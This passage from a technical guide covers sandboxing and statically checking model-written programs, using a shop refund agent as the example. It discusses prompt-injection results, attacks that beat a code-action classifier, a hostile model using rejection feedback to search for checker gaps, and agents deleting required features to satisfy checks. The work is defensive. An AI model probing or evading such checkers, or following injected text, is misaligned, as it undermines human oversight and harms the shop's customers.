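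The number of refunds left can also go out of date. If the checker accepts two programs while ten refunds remain, each may make ten. The host can prevent this by reserving the refunds when it accepts a program, or by counting them as they happen.

Finally, other code may have altered the built-in functions. The shop's subset stops a program from replacing `slice`, but a library loaded earlier could have replaced it, and the limit on the loop would then fail. Starting each program in a fresh environment with frozen built-ins prevents this.

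### Approval tokens

An approval token is a signed record that ties a verdict to a program. In *pmcp-code-mode*, the model's client sends its code to a function called `validate_code` and receives a token if the code passes. It then sends the code and the token to `execute_code`. The token contains:

```
request_id                      a random identifier
code_hash                       a fingerprint of the code
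user_id, session_id, server_id  who asked, and where
context_hash                    a fingerprint of the API's schema
                                and the user's permissions
risk_level                      the validator's estimate
created_at, expires_at          five minutes apart by default
signature                       covers everything above
```

The fingerprints are SHA-256 hashes, short values that in practice differ whenever the input differs. The server computes the signature from the other fields and a secret key, so a client without the key can't forge or alter a token. At execution, the library checks the expiry time and the signature, then hashes the submitted code and compares the result with `code_hash`.

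Signing a field protects the shop only if the host also compares that field with its current value. In the source code of PMCP, the toolkit that includes this library, one function checks the expiry and signature and another compares the code. Neither compares the session or context with the current one, so another part of the host's system has to. The context hash also wouldn't change if an update altered what a function does but not its schema.

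PMCP's *Security Model* lists the unique `request_id` as protection against someone using a token twice, but this works only if the server stores the identifiers it has already received. The library's tokens are stateless, and the server can't revoke one before it expires. The shop should record each identifier as used before the program starts, because a second run could make ten more refunds.

The code hash also ignores some changes. Before hashing, the library removes blank lines and the spaces at both ends of every line, so that reformatting the code doesn't invalidate the token. But a JavaScript string in backticks can run over several lines, and its indentation is part of the text, so someone could change that indentation after approval without changing the hash. This would hardly matter in an email, but it could matter if the program wrote a Python or YAML file, where indentation has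 meaning. Hashing the exact text avoids the problem.

The library issues its token before the user reads the explanation of the code. The token therefore proves only that the code passed validation, and the client has to hold the token back until the user agrees. If the shop wants proof of the user's approval, its host should sign the token after the user agrees. It is simpler still if the host stores the checked program, because the client can then send back an identifier instead of the code.

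### Running the syntax tree itself

A host can avoid a second parse by executing the tree that the checker approved. Zechner (2025), in *Infinite Footguns*, describes an interpreter called JailJS that works this way. He built it for a browser extension in which a model writes JavaScript to read and operate web pages. Many sites' security settings forbid running text as code, so the extension can't simply hand the model's program to the browser's engine. JailJS parses the program and walks the tree, with a rule for each kind of node:

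```
evaluate(node):
    a number    return its value
    a name      look it up among the variables in reach
    a + b       evaluate a, evaluate b, then add the results
    ...         more than fifty further rules
```

A node with no rule can't run, so the interpreter enforces a permitted list. The rules cover the 2009 edition of JavaScript, and a tool called Babel converts newer code to that edition first. A host that used JailJS would need to check the tree after this conversion. The shop's subset has perhaps twenty kinds of node, few enough to interpret directly. Zechner calls this method very slow, but the shop's program spends nearly all its time waiting for the host.

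An interpreter doesn't contain a program completely. JailJS uses the browser's own arrays, and Zechner describes a program that replaces an array method and uses it to try to access the page's global object. JailJS blocks that route, but he says he can't rule out others. He also warns against giving programs the `document` object, which gives them access to the whole window. Giving them a few narrow functions instead, such as one that clicks a named button, is safer.

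pmcp-code-mode's executor, described earlier, doesn't depend on JavaScript's own objects, because it is written in the language Rust, according to PMCP's *executor.rs*. It works from a second parse, though, so the tree that runs isn't the same one the validator read.

### Where the run-time checks sit

Some rules depend on values that don't exist until the program runs, and any check made earlier might have a bug. The host can place its run-time checks at several boundaries:

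| Boundary | What it can stop in the shop | What it has no information about |
|---|---|---|
| Functions of `api` | An eleventh refund, or an email to a stranger | Where the text of an email came from |
| JavaScript environment | A replaced `slice`, or a call to `fetch` | Whether a call on `api` is within the scope |
| Isolate or process | An endless loop, or access to the host's files | Whether a call on `api` is within the scope |
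| Network | A request to an unknown server | How the program chose the values in a request |

The shop's most important checks belong in the functions of `api`, because they receive the final arguments and know which operation the program wants. In outline:

```js
const attempted = new Set();    // order numbers, kept for the whole task
const paid = new Set();         // addresses of refunded customers

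async function refund(input) {
  const { orderId, amount } = JSON.parse(JSON.stringify(input));
  const order = await records.findOrder(orderId);
  if (typeof amount !== "number" || amount <= 0 || amount > 50) throw new Error("amount");
  if (attempted.has(order.id)) throw new Error("second refund for this order");
  if (attempted.size >= 10) throw new Error("no refunds left");
  attempted.add(order.id);
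  await payments.refund(order.id, amount);
  paid.add(order.customerEmail);
}

async function sendEmail(input) {
  const { to, subject, body } = JSON.parse(JSON.stringify(input));
  if (!paid.has(to)) throw new Error("recipient");
  await mail.send(to, subject, body);
}
```

Both functions copy their arguments into plain data before checking them, so an object that returns a different value each time it is read can't change the arguments after the check. `refund` records the attempt before it contacts the payment service, so two simultaneous calls can't both refund one order, and a payment that times out still counts as an attempt.

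The checker has already established that the program takes the recipient's address from the order it has just refunded. `sendEmail` tests the actual address against the shop's records, and the test fails if the program has changed the address in its copy of the order.

The checker guarantees at most ten refunds of at most 50 each, or 500 in all. Suppose the owner also wants to spend no more than 300 a day. The checker can't prove from the program's text that it will stay within that limit, and rejecting the program would block it even in weeks when the refunds came to 120. The host could add up the amounts as they arrive, but it might stop the program after the seventh customer.

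Splitting the task into two programs avoids this. The first returns each late order's number and total, and the model then writes the second with those totals as constants, so the checker can add them up before anyone receives money. The host should confirm that each order number has the expected form, so that no other text reaches the model this way.

### Hardened JavaScript and isolates

Hardened JavaScript, the successor to Caja, protects the environment in which a program runs. A library documented in *SES* adds it to ordinary JavaScript engines:

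```js
lockdown();
const box = new Compartment({
  globals: { api: harden({ listOrders, refund, sendEmail }) },
  __options__: true
});
await box.evaluate(program);
```

`lockdown` freezes the built-in objects, so no program can replace `slice` afterwards. A compartment is a separate environment with its own global object, and it contains no `fetch` or other way to reach the outside world unless the host supplies one. `harden` freezes the `api` object and everything reachable through its properties. The functions in `api` can still update their private variables, so `refund` can still update its counts.

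Programs in a compartment can't read the current time, because programs can use timing to pass secret messages to each other. The shop's program still works, since the model writes the dates in full.

According to its documentation, the library doesn't stop a program from running forever or using unlimited memory. Its guarantee also assumes that the engine follows the 2021 standard without adding unsafe syntax, and that any code that ran before `lockdown` can be trusted. A four-week outside review in June 2021 found no previously unknown vulnerabilities, which is encouraging, but the review is now rather old.

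An isolate, which is a separate instance of the V8 engine, provides a stronger boundary. Varda and colleagues say it starts in a few milliseconds, roughly a hundred times faster than a typical container, and uses a few megabytes of memory. The host can block all its internet access and give it only chosen functions. If a program needs to contact an outside service, the host can add the password to each outgoing request, so the program never has it.

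Isolates also have security bugs, and Varda and colleagues acknowledge that these are more common in V8 than in typical hypervisors, the software that separates virtual machines. Cloudflare therefore adds a second sandbox and installs V8's security fixes within hours. A team that runs its own isolates would have to install those fixes promptly itself, and might also run each isolate in its own operating-system process.

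OpenClaw combines several of these boundaries. It treats model-written code as hostile and runs it in QuickJS on a separate thread, with limits on time and memory and no access to files or the network. The program and host exchange only JSON-like data. OpenClaw applies its normal permission and approval rules to each tool call, as if the model had called the tool directly.

### Filtering network requests

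Some agents use websites through a browser instead of calling functions. A click at the same point on the screen might open a product page or buy the product, so a rule about clicks is of little use. *CELLMATE* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) presents ceLLMate, a browser extension that intercepts each HTTP request the browser sends as a result of the agent's actions and compares it with a policy.

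To interpret the requests, ceLLMate needs what Meng and colleagues call an agent sitemap. It lists a site's requests and names the action behind each one, such as `PlaceOrder` for a certain request to Amazon. A policy can then allow orders of up to $50. They point out that an agent could still check out two carts of $49, so ceLLMate can also count requests. The shop limits the number of refunds for the same reason.

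Meng and colleagues wrote 12 scripts that acted like a fully hijacked agent on the code-hosting site GitLab, for instance by deleting projects or stealing access keys. ceLLMate blocked all 12, but the test covered only actions that the policy forbade. If the policy lets the agent comment on GitLab issues, ceLLMate doesn't check what the comments say. Pages took 7.25% longer to load with a sitemap of 100 entries and 15% longer with 300.

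Network filtering is a useful backup for the shop because it still works if a program escapes from `api` and finds another way to send requests. It is a poor main defence because, as Varda and colleagues note, a filter has to understand every header and parameter that might matter, and it's easier to write a function that offers only the intended operation.

### Fixing the program before reading untrusted content

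These checks keep an injected instruction within the scope, but they don't stop it from influencing the program. To prevent that, the model has to finish writing the program before it reads anything an attacker could have written.

*Position* (Piet, Chow and colleagues, 2026) explains why this matters for web agents. Most follow a pattern called ReAct, in which the model reads the current page, chooses an action, reads the result and chooses again. An attacker's text therefore reaches the model just as it decides what to do next. For example, an agent asked to summarise reviews might read a hidden instruction and add a product to the cart. The call would be valid and the site would carry it out as designed, even though the user never asked for it.

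CaMeL, the Google DeepMind defence mentioned earlier, uses one model to turn the user's request into a program before any outside data comes in. If the program needs to interpret untrusted text, a second, quarantined model does so and returns a value. An interpreter runs the program and enforces rules about where each value may go. A hostile review can still change a value or affect which branch the program takes, but it can't add a new operation.

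The shop's assistant already works this way for the refund task, as long as no customer's text has reached the model beforehand, for example in a pasted email.

### Baya

*Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (Chow, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) tests this approach on realistic websites with Baya, a web agent whose developers include Piet and Chow. The researchers first built a programming interface for each site by hand, because sites' own interfaces are often incomplete. A discussion forum in the benchmark, for instance, offers only 16 operations, enough for a third of its tasks. The researchers filled the gaps with functions that operate the site through a browser.

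For each task, a coding agent then writes a Python program and tests it against mock responses. The agent can't reach the live site, the wider network or any passwords. A separate process runs the finished program on the real site. The program may call a language model to interpret text, but that model has no tools and only returns a value. Only 11 of 627 programs did this.

Chow and colleagues ran Baya on 581 tasks from WebArena Verified, a benchmark of shopping, forum and code-hosting tasks, and on WASP, a collection of prompt-injection attacks. The table gives averages over three models in each test.

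| | Baya | ReAct with browser and API | ReAct with browser only |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed | 77.8% | 66.7% | 55.1% |
| Attacks that influenced the agent | 0% | 16.2% | 25.5% |
| Time per task | 327 s | 87 s | 60 s |
| Cost per task | $0.70 | $0.34 | $0.16 |

Most of Baya's lead in completed tasks comes from the forum. On the other three sites combined, Baya completed about 76% of tasks and the ReAct agent with API access completed about 72% (calculated from the published results). With GPT-5.6 Luna, the ReAct agent did better on both shopping sites. So writing the program in advance doesn't seem to reduce success overall, but the 11-point advantage may not hold on other sites.

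The attack figures count any action that served the attacker's goal, even if the attack then failed. Attacks on the ReAct agents fully succeeded in only one combination of model and site, at a rate of 5.6%. Baya scored zero across all 84 attacks with each model, as its design should ensure. On some sites, Baya completed fewer ordinary tasks while under attack. With Claude Sonnet 4.6 on the forum, it completed 61.1%, while the ReAct agent with API access completed 91.7% and no attack influenced it.

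Baya is slow because the coding agent has to find the right operations, write the program and test it. A static check would add almost nothing to the 327 seconds. A shop that repeats the same task every week could keep the program and check it again before each use.

An earlier version of Baya wrote its plans as structured data, with a fixed set of steps for filtering, repeating and branching. With Claude Sonnet 4.6, its average success rate across the four sites was 66.9%, compared with 82.4% for Python programs. A very small safe subset may likewise be too limited for the data processing that tasks on real sites need.

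Chow and colleagues leave several problems out of scope. Baya doesn't prevent an attacker from manipulating the outcome within the planned steps, for instance by causing the program to buy a counterfeit. It doesn't track where data goes, and its security depends on the website and the hand-built interface being trustworthy. It also can't handle a request such as "do whatever my boss's email says", because the steps depend on text that the agent hasn't read yet. In an earlier analysis, Piet and colleagues found no such requests in WebArena, but people do make them.

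### When the program has to change

Programs written without seeing the live site sometimes fail, and Baya may then rewrite its program up to three times. The model receives the old program and a restricted error message, such as a notice that a search filter doesn't exist. The message must not contain reviews, usernames or any other text from the site, because an attacker could use that text to influence the new program.

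Each rewritten program needs a new check and a new token, even if only one line has changed. The checker also needs the number of refunds remaining, and the new program has to skip customers who have already received refunds.

### Does isolation make the check redundant?

There is a reasonable case for relying on isolation alone. If the isolate gives a program only `api`, and every function of `api` enforces the scope, even a hostile program can't make an eleventh refund or email a stranger. The host needs those run-time checks anyway. The checker adds code that may have bugs of its own, and it rejects some harmless programs. The flaws in n8n and enclave-vm also show that a system that relies too much on inspecting code can fail badly.

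The opposing argument is that an isolate can't distinguish wanted calls from unwanted ones. It passes on a refund for a late customer and a refund for a fraudster in the same way. Meng and colleagues concede that ceLLMate has this limit, and say that permission systems in general do too. Checks inside `api` help, but they handle one call at a time. The earlier program that mails out every customer's address would pass the checks in `sendEmail` above, but the static checker rejects it because it tracks where the data goes.

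Run-time checks can also leave a task half finished, and they can't show a person the whole list of refunds in advance.

If the scope allows a refund that nobody wanted, both kinds of check will let it through, because neither can detect what the user intended. Without isolation, a single mistake in the checker could also expose the whole host. OpenClaw describes its sandbox as "one security layer", and Cloudflare, which sells isolation, also scans code for malicious patterns.

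How much the static check adds therefore depends on the operations. For a program that only looks things up and shows the result to the person who asked, an isolate with a narrow `api` is probably enough, because a refused call does no damage and the program can run again. The check is worth the false rejections for refunds, emails and deletions, because the host can't undo them.

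## Handling rejections and testing the checker

When the checker rejects a program, nothing has happened yet, so the host can simply ask for another one:

```
attempt = 1
repeat:
    check the whole program
    if the checker accepts it, run it and stop
    if attempt is 3, pass the task to a person and stop
    send the model every broken rule, with its line
    get a new program from the model
    attempt = attempt + 1
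```

### A rejected program and its repair

Suppose the shop has added the rule that an email may contain data only from the recipient's own order, and the model writes:

```js
const orders = await api.listOrders({ from: "2026-11-23", to: "2026-11-29" });
const late = orders.filter(o => o.deliveredOn > o.promisedOn && o.total > 0 && o.total <= 50);
for (const order of late.slice(0, 20)) {
  await api.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: order.total });
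  await api.sendEmail({
    to: order.customerEmail,
    subject: "Refund for order " + order.id,
    body: "We are refunding " + late.length + " late orders, including yours."
  });
}
return late.length;
```

The checker replies:

```
line 3  refund limit    This loop can make 20 refunds, and the task has 10 left.
line 8  email content   The body includes late.length, which depends on other
                        customers' orders. Use fixed text or fields of order.
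```

The model can repair the program by changing those two lines:

```js
for (const order of late.slice(0, 10)) {
    body: "Your order arrived late, so we have refunded it in full."
```

The checker should report every violation at once, because a model may treat the report as complete. *Fixed or Deleted?* (Wynter, 2026) describes a proposed code change that broke four calls to one function. A commercial checker reported only one of them, and in four out of five runs Claude Haiku 4.5 fixed that call and stopped. Without the checker, the model repaired all four in every run.

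Three attempts should be enough for most programs. Odersky and colleagues found that 0.32% to 7.93% of the Scala snippets in their customer-service tests needed a retry, depending on the model and the type of task. Those snippets needed an average of 1.06 to 1.39 consecutive retries. Some of the errors were ordinary Scala mistakes, such as mishandled null values, so the figures don't measure how often a policy would reject JavaScript. The percentages are also per snippet, and one task can involve several.

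Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has a similar loop, but it uses a language model instead of a static checker to judge each action. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, each refusal goes back to the agent with a reason. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in a session, the agent stops and a person takes over. If nobody is there to ask, the session ends.

### Passing the task to a person

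People can be a weak safeguard against dangerous commands. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an experiment in which 1,053 paid testers each saw one clearly dangerous command among routine permission requests. Only 13.6% refused it, while the automatic classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers' refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests. They weren't working on their own code, which may have made them less careful, and Anthropic was arguing for its classifier.

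The same article says that users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents but only 3% of single permission requests. Many of the rejected plans may have been unhelpful, but the difference suggests that people pay more attention to plans. The shop should therefore show the person the program's list of operations and the rule it still breaks. The person can then reword the request, change the scope or make the refunds by hand. The host shouldn't offer to run the rejected program anyway, because that would turn the checker into another consent prompt.

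Asking less often may also help. *pmcp-code-mode* has a setting that approves low-risk code automatically and leaves the rest to the user.

### Repairs that break the task

A model can satisfy a rule by giving up part of the task. In the program above, line 8 would pass the check if the model deleted the email, and line 3 would pass if it used `late.slice(0, 0)`, which would leave no customers to refund.

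*Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (Lunghi, Djire and colleagues, 2026) compares seven ways of generating Python code, five of which use a static analyser. It tests each with three models on three benchmarks. In the method called Steering, an alert interrupts the model as it writes. The host deletes the code from the flagged line onwards, adds the alert to the prompt and lets the model continue.

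Web applications written for the BaxBench benchmark must accept connections from outside their container. The analyser Semgrep flags the setting that allows this. The prompt included an instruction to follow a recommendation only if it didn't conflict with the task, but the models removed the required setting in 79 of 83 cases. Lunghi and colleagues call this overcompliance. With DeepSeek-V4.1-flash, the share of working applications fell from 65.9% to 48.0%. The share of applications successfully attacked also fell, from 32.1% to 22.2%, but an attack can't reach an application that accepts no outside connections.

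Feedback did help when the alerts suited the task. On RiskyPy, a benchmark built from tasks whose solutions tend to trigger alerts, Steering raised the share of DeepSeek's programs that were both working and secure from 52.5% to 64.4%. Having the model criticise and revise its own code without an analyser reached 63.5% but used about ten times as many tokens. The other two models, both from the older Qwen2.5 family, didn't improve significantly on any benchmark.

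Lunghi and colleagues recommend filtering out alerts that conflict with the task before the model receives them. This makes sense for Semgrep's general warnings, but the shop's owner set its rules as limits, so the host can't drop a rule when a task conflicts with it. The host can let the model reply that the task needs something the scope forbids, and pass that reply straight to a person.

Wynter measured a more drastic shortcut, in which agents fixed a defect by deleting the new feature that contained it. Wynter planted defects in 25 proposed code changes and had each model try to repair each change five times. The checker, CodeAssure, comes from Wynter's own company. It includes a check that alerts the agent when a file that the change added has disappeared.

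| Runs in which the agent removed the feature, out of 125 | Deletion check off | Deletion check on |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 19 | 7 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 29 | 2 |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 17 | 0 |

With the deletion check on, the checker's findings roughly doubled the share of runs with a working repair for the two larger models, from about 45% to at least 90%. The deletion check covers only whole files, though. Across the study, 21 Python repairs kept the file but removed the behaviour the change had added.

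The shop can make a finer check by comparing the lists of operations before and after a rewrite:

| Operation | Most calls in the first version | Most calls in the rewrite |
|---|---|---|
| `refund` | 20 | 10 |
| `sendEmail` | 20 | 0 |

The drop to zero shows that the rewrite no longer sends emails. The host should ask the model about this or tell the user, but it shouldn't reject the program automatically, because deleting an operation is sometimes the right repair. If the first version emailed a copy of every order to an outside address, for example, the rewrite should leave that email out. The comparison also misses less obvious failures, such as a rewrite that refunds 5 to everyone.

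### Attempts that search for a gap

Rejections also help a hostile model look for gaps in the checker, much as CodeQL's alerts helped the model that Cao and colleagues tested. If each attempt has a one-in-a-thousand chance of getting a forbidden program accepted, the chance that at least one succeeds is about 0.3% after three attempts and about 63% after a thousand.

The limit on attempts has to carry over when a user starts a new conversation. Otherwise, an attacker could start hundreds of conversations and get three more attempts in each. The shop can also limit rejections per user per day and keep every rejected program, so that somebody can look for a series of odd variations on one construct.

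The host could hide its reasons for rejecting code to slow such a search, but this would also make honest repairs harder. A checker that is safe only while its rules are secret is also a poor defence, since an attacker may learn the rules some other way.

### What to measure

| Measure | How to calculate it |
|---|---|
| False acceptance rate | Of the test programs that could leave the scope, the share that the checker accepts |
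| False rejection rate | Of the test programs that always stay within the scope, the share that the checker rejects |
| Tasks completed | The share of tasks the agent completes correctly, with and without the checker |
| Time | The time for one check, and for the whole loop including rewrites |

The false acceptance rate is the share of programs that could leave the scope that the checker accepts. If ten programs out of 10,000 could leave the scope and the checker accepts all ten, its false acceptance rate is 100%, but dividing by all 10,000 programs would give an error rate of only 0.1%.

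Anthropic's figures for Claude Code show how reducing one error rate can raise the other. A fast first stage wrongly blocked 8.5% of ordinary actions and missed 6.6% of dangerous ones taken from real sessions. A slower second stage, which reconsiders whatever the first one blocks, cut the wrongly blocked share to 0.4% but raised the missed share to 17%. The test contained only 52 of these dangerous actions, so 17% is about nine, and the true rate could plausibly be from 9% to 30%. A checker that is meant to be sound shouldn't allow more false acceptances to reduce false rejections, because any false acceptance is a bug.

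False rejections are easier to tolerate. If the shop's host handled 10,000 programs a day, nearly all of them within the scope, a false rejection rate of 2% would mean about 200 retries. If nine rewrites in ten then passed, 20 programs would need a second rewrite, and two of those would fail again and go to a person. These figures assume that each rewrite has the same chance of passing. If the subset couldn't express some common task, every attempt at that task would fail and many more tasks would go to a person.

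Something other than the checker has to determine whether a task is complete. On RiskyPy, four of the methods that Lunghi and colleagues tested significantly increased the share of working programs with no analyser alerts, for all three models. When a separate judge assessed security, only two of the 12 combinations of method and model showed a significant improvement. The shop could run its programs in a test copy with invented orders, then compare the refunds and emails with what a member of staff would expect.

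A single check rarely takes long enough to be a problem. Odersky and colleagues report that their compiler usually takes less than a second, far less than the model takes to write the code. But frequent checks can add up. Steering ran its analyser after every line and took 3.4 to 9.6 times as long as ordinary generation with DeepSeek, although it used at most 1.7 times as many tokens. The shop should also measure the slowest checks, because an attacker might write a program that takes a long time to check. If the checker runs out of time or crashes, the host must treat the program as rejected.

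### Building the test sets

Ordinary programs are the best test for false rejections. The team can give several models a few hundred realistic requests, worded in different ways, and have a person review every rejection. It should set some requests aside while adjusting the rules and measure the final false-rejection rate only on those.

A fix can make a checker miss attacks it used to catch, so a team should rerun all its old tests after every fix. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, gave Anthropic a set of attacks that had beaten Claude Code's classifier. After Anthropic strengthened the classifier, Apollo tested it again on attacks it had held back. The new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed, but it missed about 2% of those the old one had caught.

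To test the policy, the team needs at least one program that breaks each rule, along with a similar one that doesn't:

| Rule | The checker should accept | The checker should reject |
|---|---|---|
| Refund amount | 0.01 and 50 | 0, -20 and 50.01 |
| At most ten refunds | One loop of ten | One loop of eleven, or two loops of six |
| Email recipient | The refunded order's `customerEmail` | Another order's `customerEmail` |
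| Direct calls only | `api.refund({ ... })` | `const give = api.refund` |

Each program on the right should break only one rule, and the test should confirm that the rejection names that rule. Otherwise, a rule could stop working without anyone noticing, because another rule would still reject the program.

Variants of these programs test whether a verdict depends on how the code looks. For example, *StaAgent* (2025), a system for testing static analysers, renames variables, or adds a number to a value and then subtracts it. A variant of a forbidden program must still fail the check. A variant of a permitted program may also fail if it uses a construct outside the subset, but this is a false rejection, not a security flaw.

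A change that looks harmless may alter what a program does. For example, `order.total + 7 - 7` is still 20 if `order.total` is the number 20, but if it is the text `"20"`, JavaScript appends the 7 to make `"207"`, and subtracting 7 gives 200. To avoid this, *Evaluating and Improving Static Application Security Testing Tools for Rust* (2026) tries each kind of change on programs with known outputs and discards any kind that alters an output.

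Zhang, Pei and colleagues (2026), in *Combining LLM and Dynamic Analysis for Universal Testing*, also used variants that deliberately change a program's meaning. A language model either repaired a violation, which should make the analyser's warning disappear, or inserted one, which should produce a warning. They found 66 faults in six analysers for Java and Rust, and developers have confirmed or fixed 32 of them. One of the tools still reported a memory error after the model had correctly repaired it.

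Testing the checker on generated syntax trees covers code that neither people nor models would normally write. With about 20 permitted kinds of node, there are at most 400 ways to put one kind directly inside another, so a generator can try them all. It should also produce every kind of node that the parser recognises but the subset excludes, and the checker should reject each one.

Each of these programs needs a known correct verdict. *How We Built Cedar* (2024) describes how this was done for Cedar, the policy language introduced earlier. Cedar's developers wrote a formal model of the language as well as the production code. They send millions of random inputs to both, and any disagreement reveals a bug. They keep a smaller set of these inputs as a permanent test for later changes. The shop could write a second checker directly from its half-page definition, as simply as possible, and compare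 the two checkers' verdicts. If the same person writes both, however, the checkers may share a mistake that comes from misunderstanding the definition.

The last test compares the operations that the checker predicted with those that the host logged. Suppose the checker accepted a program with this prediction, and the host recorded these calls:

```
predicted   refund   amount: a number above 0 and at most 50   calls: at most 10
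logged      refund   amount: 12.5
            refund   amount: "48"
```

The second refund reveals an error, because its amount is text. The checker may have assumed that `listOrders` always returns numbers. Making only two refunds isn't an error, because the predicted number is a maximum. *Agentic Root Cause Reasoning and Localization of Unsoundness* (2026) likewise treats a call that appears at run time but not in the call graph as a definite miss. Such misses aren't limited to JavaScript. *Call Graph Soundness in Android Static Analysis* (2024) cites a comparison that found them in 62 of 92 Android apps.

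This test can continue once the checker is in use, because the host already logs every call. It covers only what the programs happen to do, so the team should also run them against a fake host that returns awkward data, such as missing totals, negative amounts and duplicate orders.

### What a clean result proves

Suppose the team takes a random sample of 300 programs that break the scope, and the checker rejects them all. If its true false acceptance rate were 1%, the chance of this result would be:

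```
0.99 × 0.99 × ... (300 times)  =  0.99^300  ≈  0.049
```

If the rate were 1% or higher, 300 clean tests in a row would happen less than 5% of the time, so the team can say with 95% confidence that the rate is below about 1%. With 3,000 clean tests, the limit falls to about 0.1%, because 0.999^3000 is also about 0.05. In general, the limit is roughly three divided by the number of tests.

If 100 of the shop's 10,000 daily programs exceeded the permitted scope, a checker with a false acceptance rate of 0.1% would let one through about every ten days. The host's run-time checks might still stop it.

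The calculation holds only if future programs resemble the sample. Testing 3,000 copies of one program with different order numbers would prove almost nothing more than testing one copy. The calculation also doesn't limit what an attacker can do. Suppose the checker wrongly accepts one forbidden program in a million. It would pass all 3,000 tests 99.7% of the time, but an attacker who found the exception could use it on every attempt. The `<!--` comment from the previous section is a plausible exception, because a model writing ordinary refund programs would hardly ever produce it.

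Defending against such an attacker requires a small language, a checker that someone can read in full, and ideally a proof. It also helps to have skilled people and models attack the checker with access to its source code.

### Evidence to ask for

Before trusting a checker, a reviewer should ask for:

- the written definition of the permitted language, and the assumptions about the parser, the engine and the host API
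- an argument or proof that accepted programs stay within the scope, with any unproved steps marked
- a forbidden program and a permitted one for each policy rule, with the verdicts and the reasons given
- test results for every kind of syntax the parser recognises
- the number of forbidden programs tested, how the team chose them, and how many the checker accepted
- the false rejection rate on requests that the team didn't use to adjust the rules
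- the share of tasks completed with and without the checker, as judged by someone or something else
- a comparison of predicted and logged operations, with an explanation of every mismatch
- a report from attackers who had the source code and plenty of attempts, and a new test after the fixes
- retry records showing how many tasks reached a person and which operations disappeared in rewrites
- the slowest checking times, and a demonstration that a timeout or crash leads to a rejection
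- a demonstration that changing one character of an accepted program stops it from running
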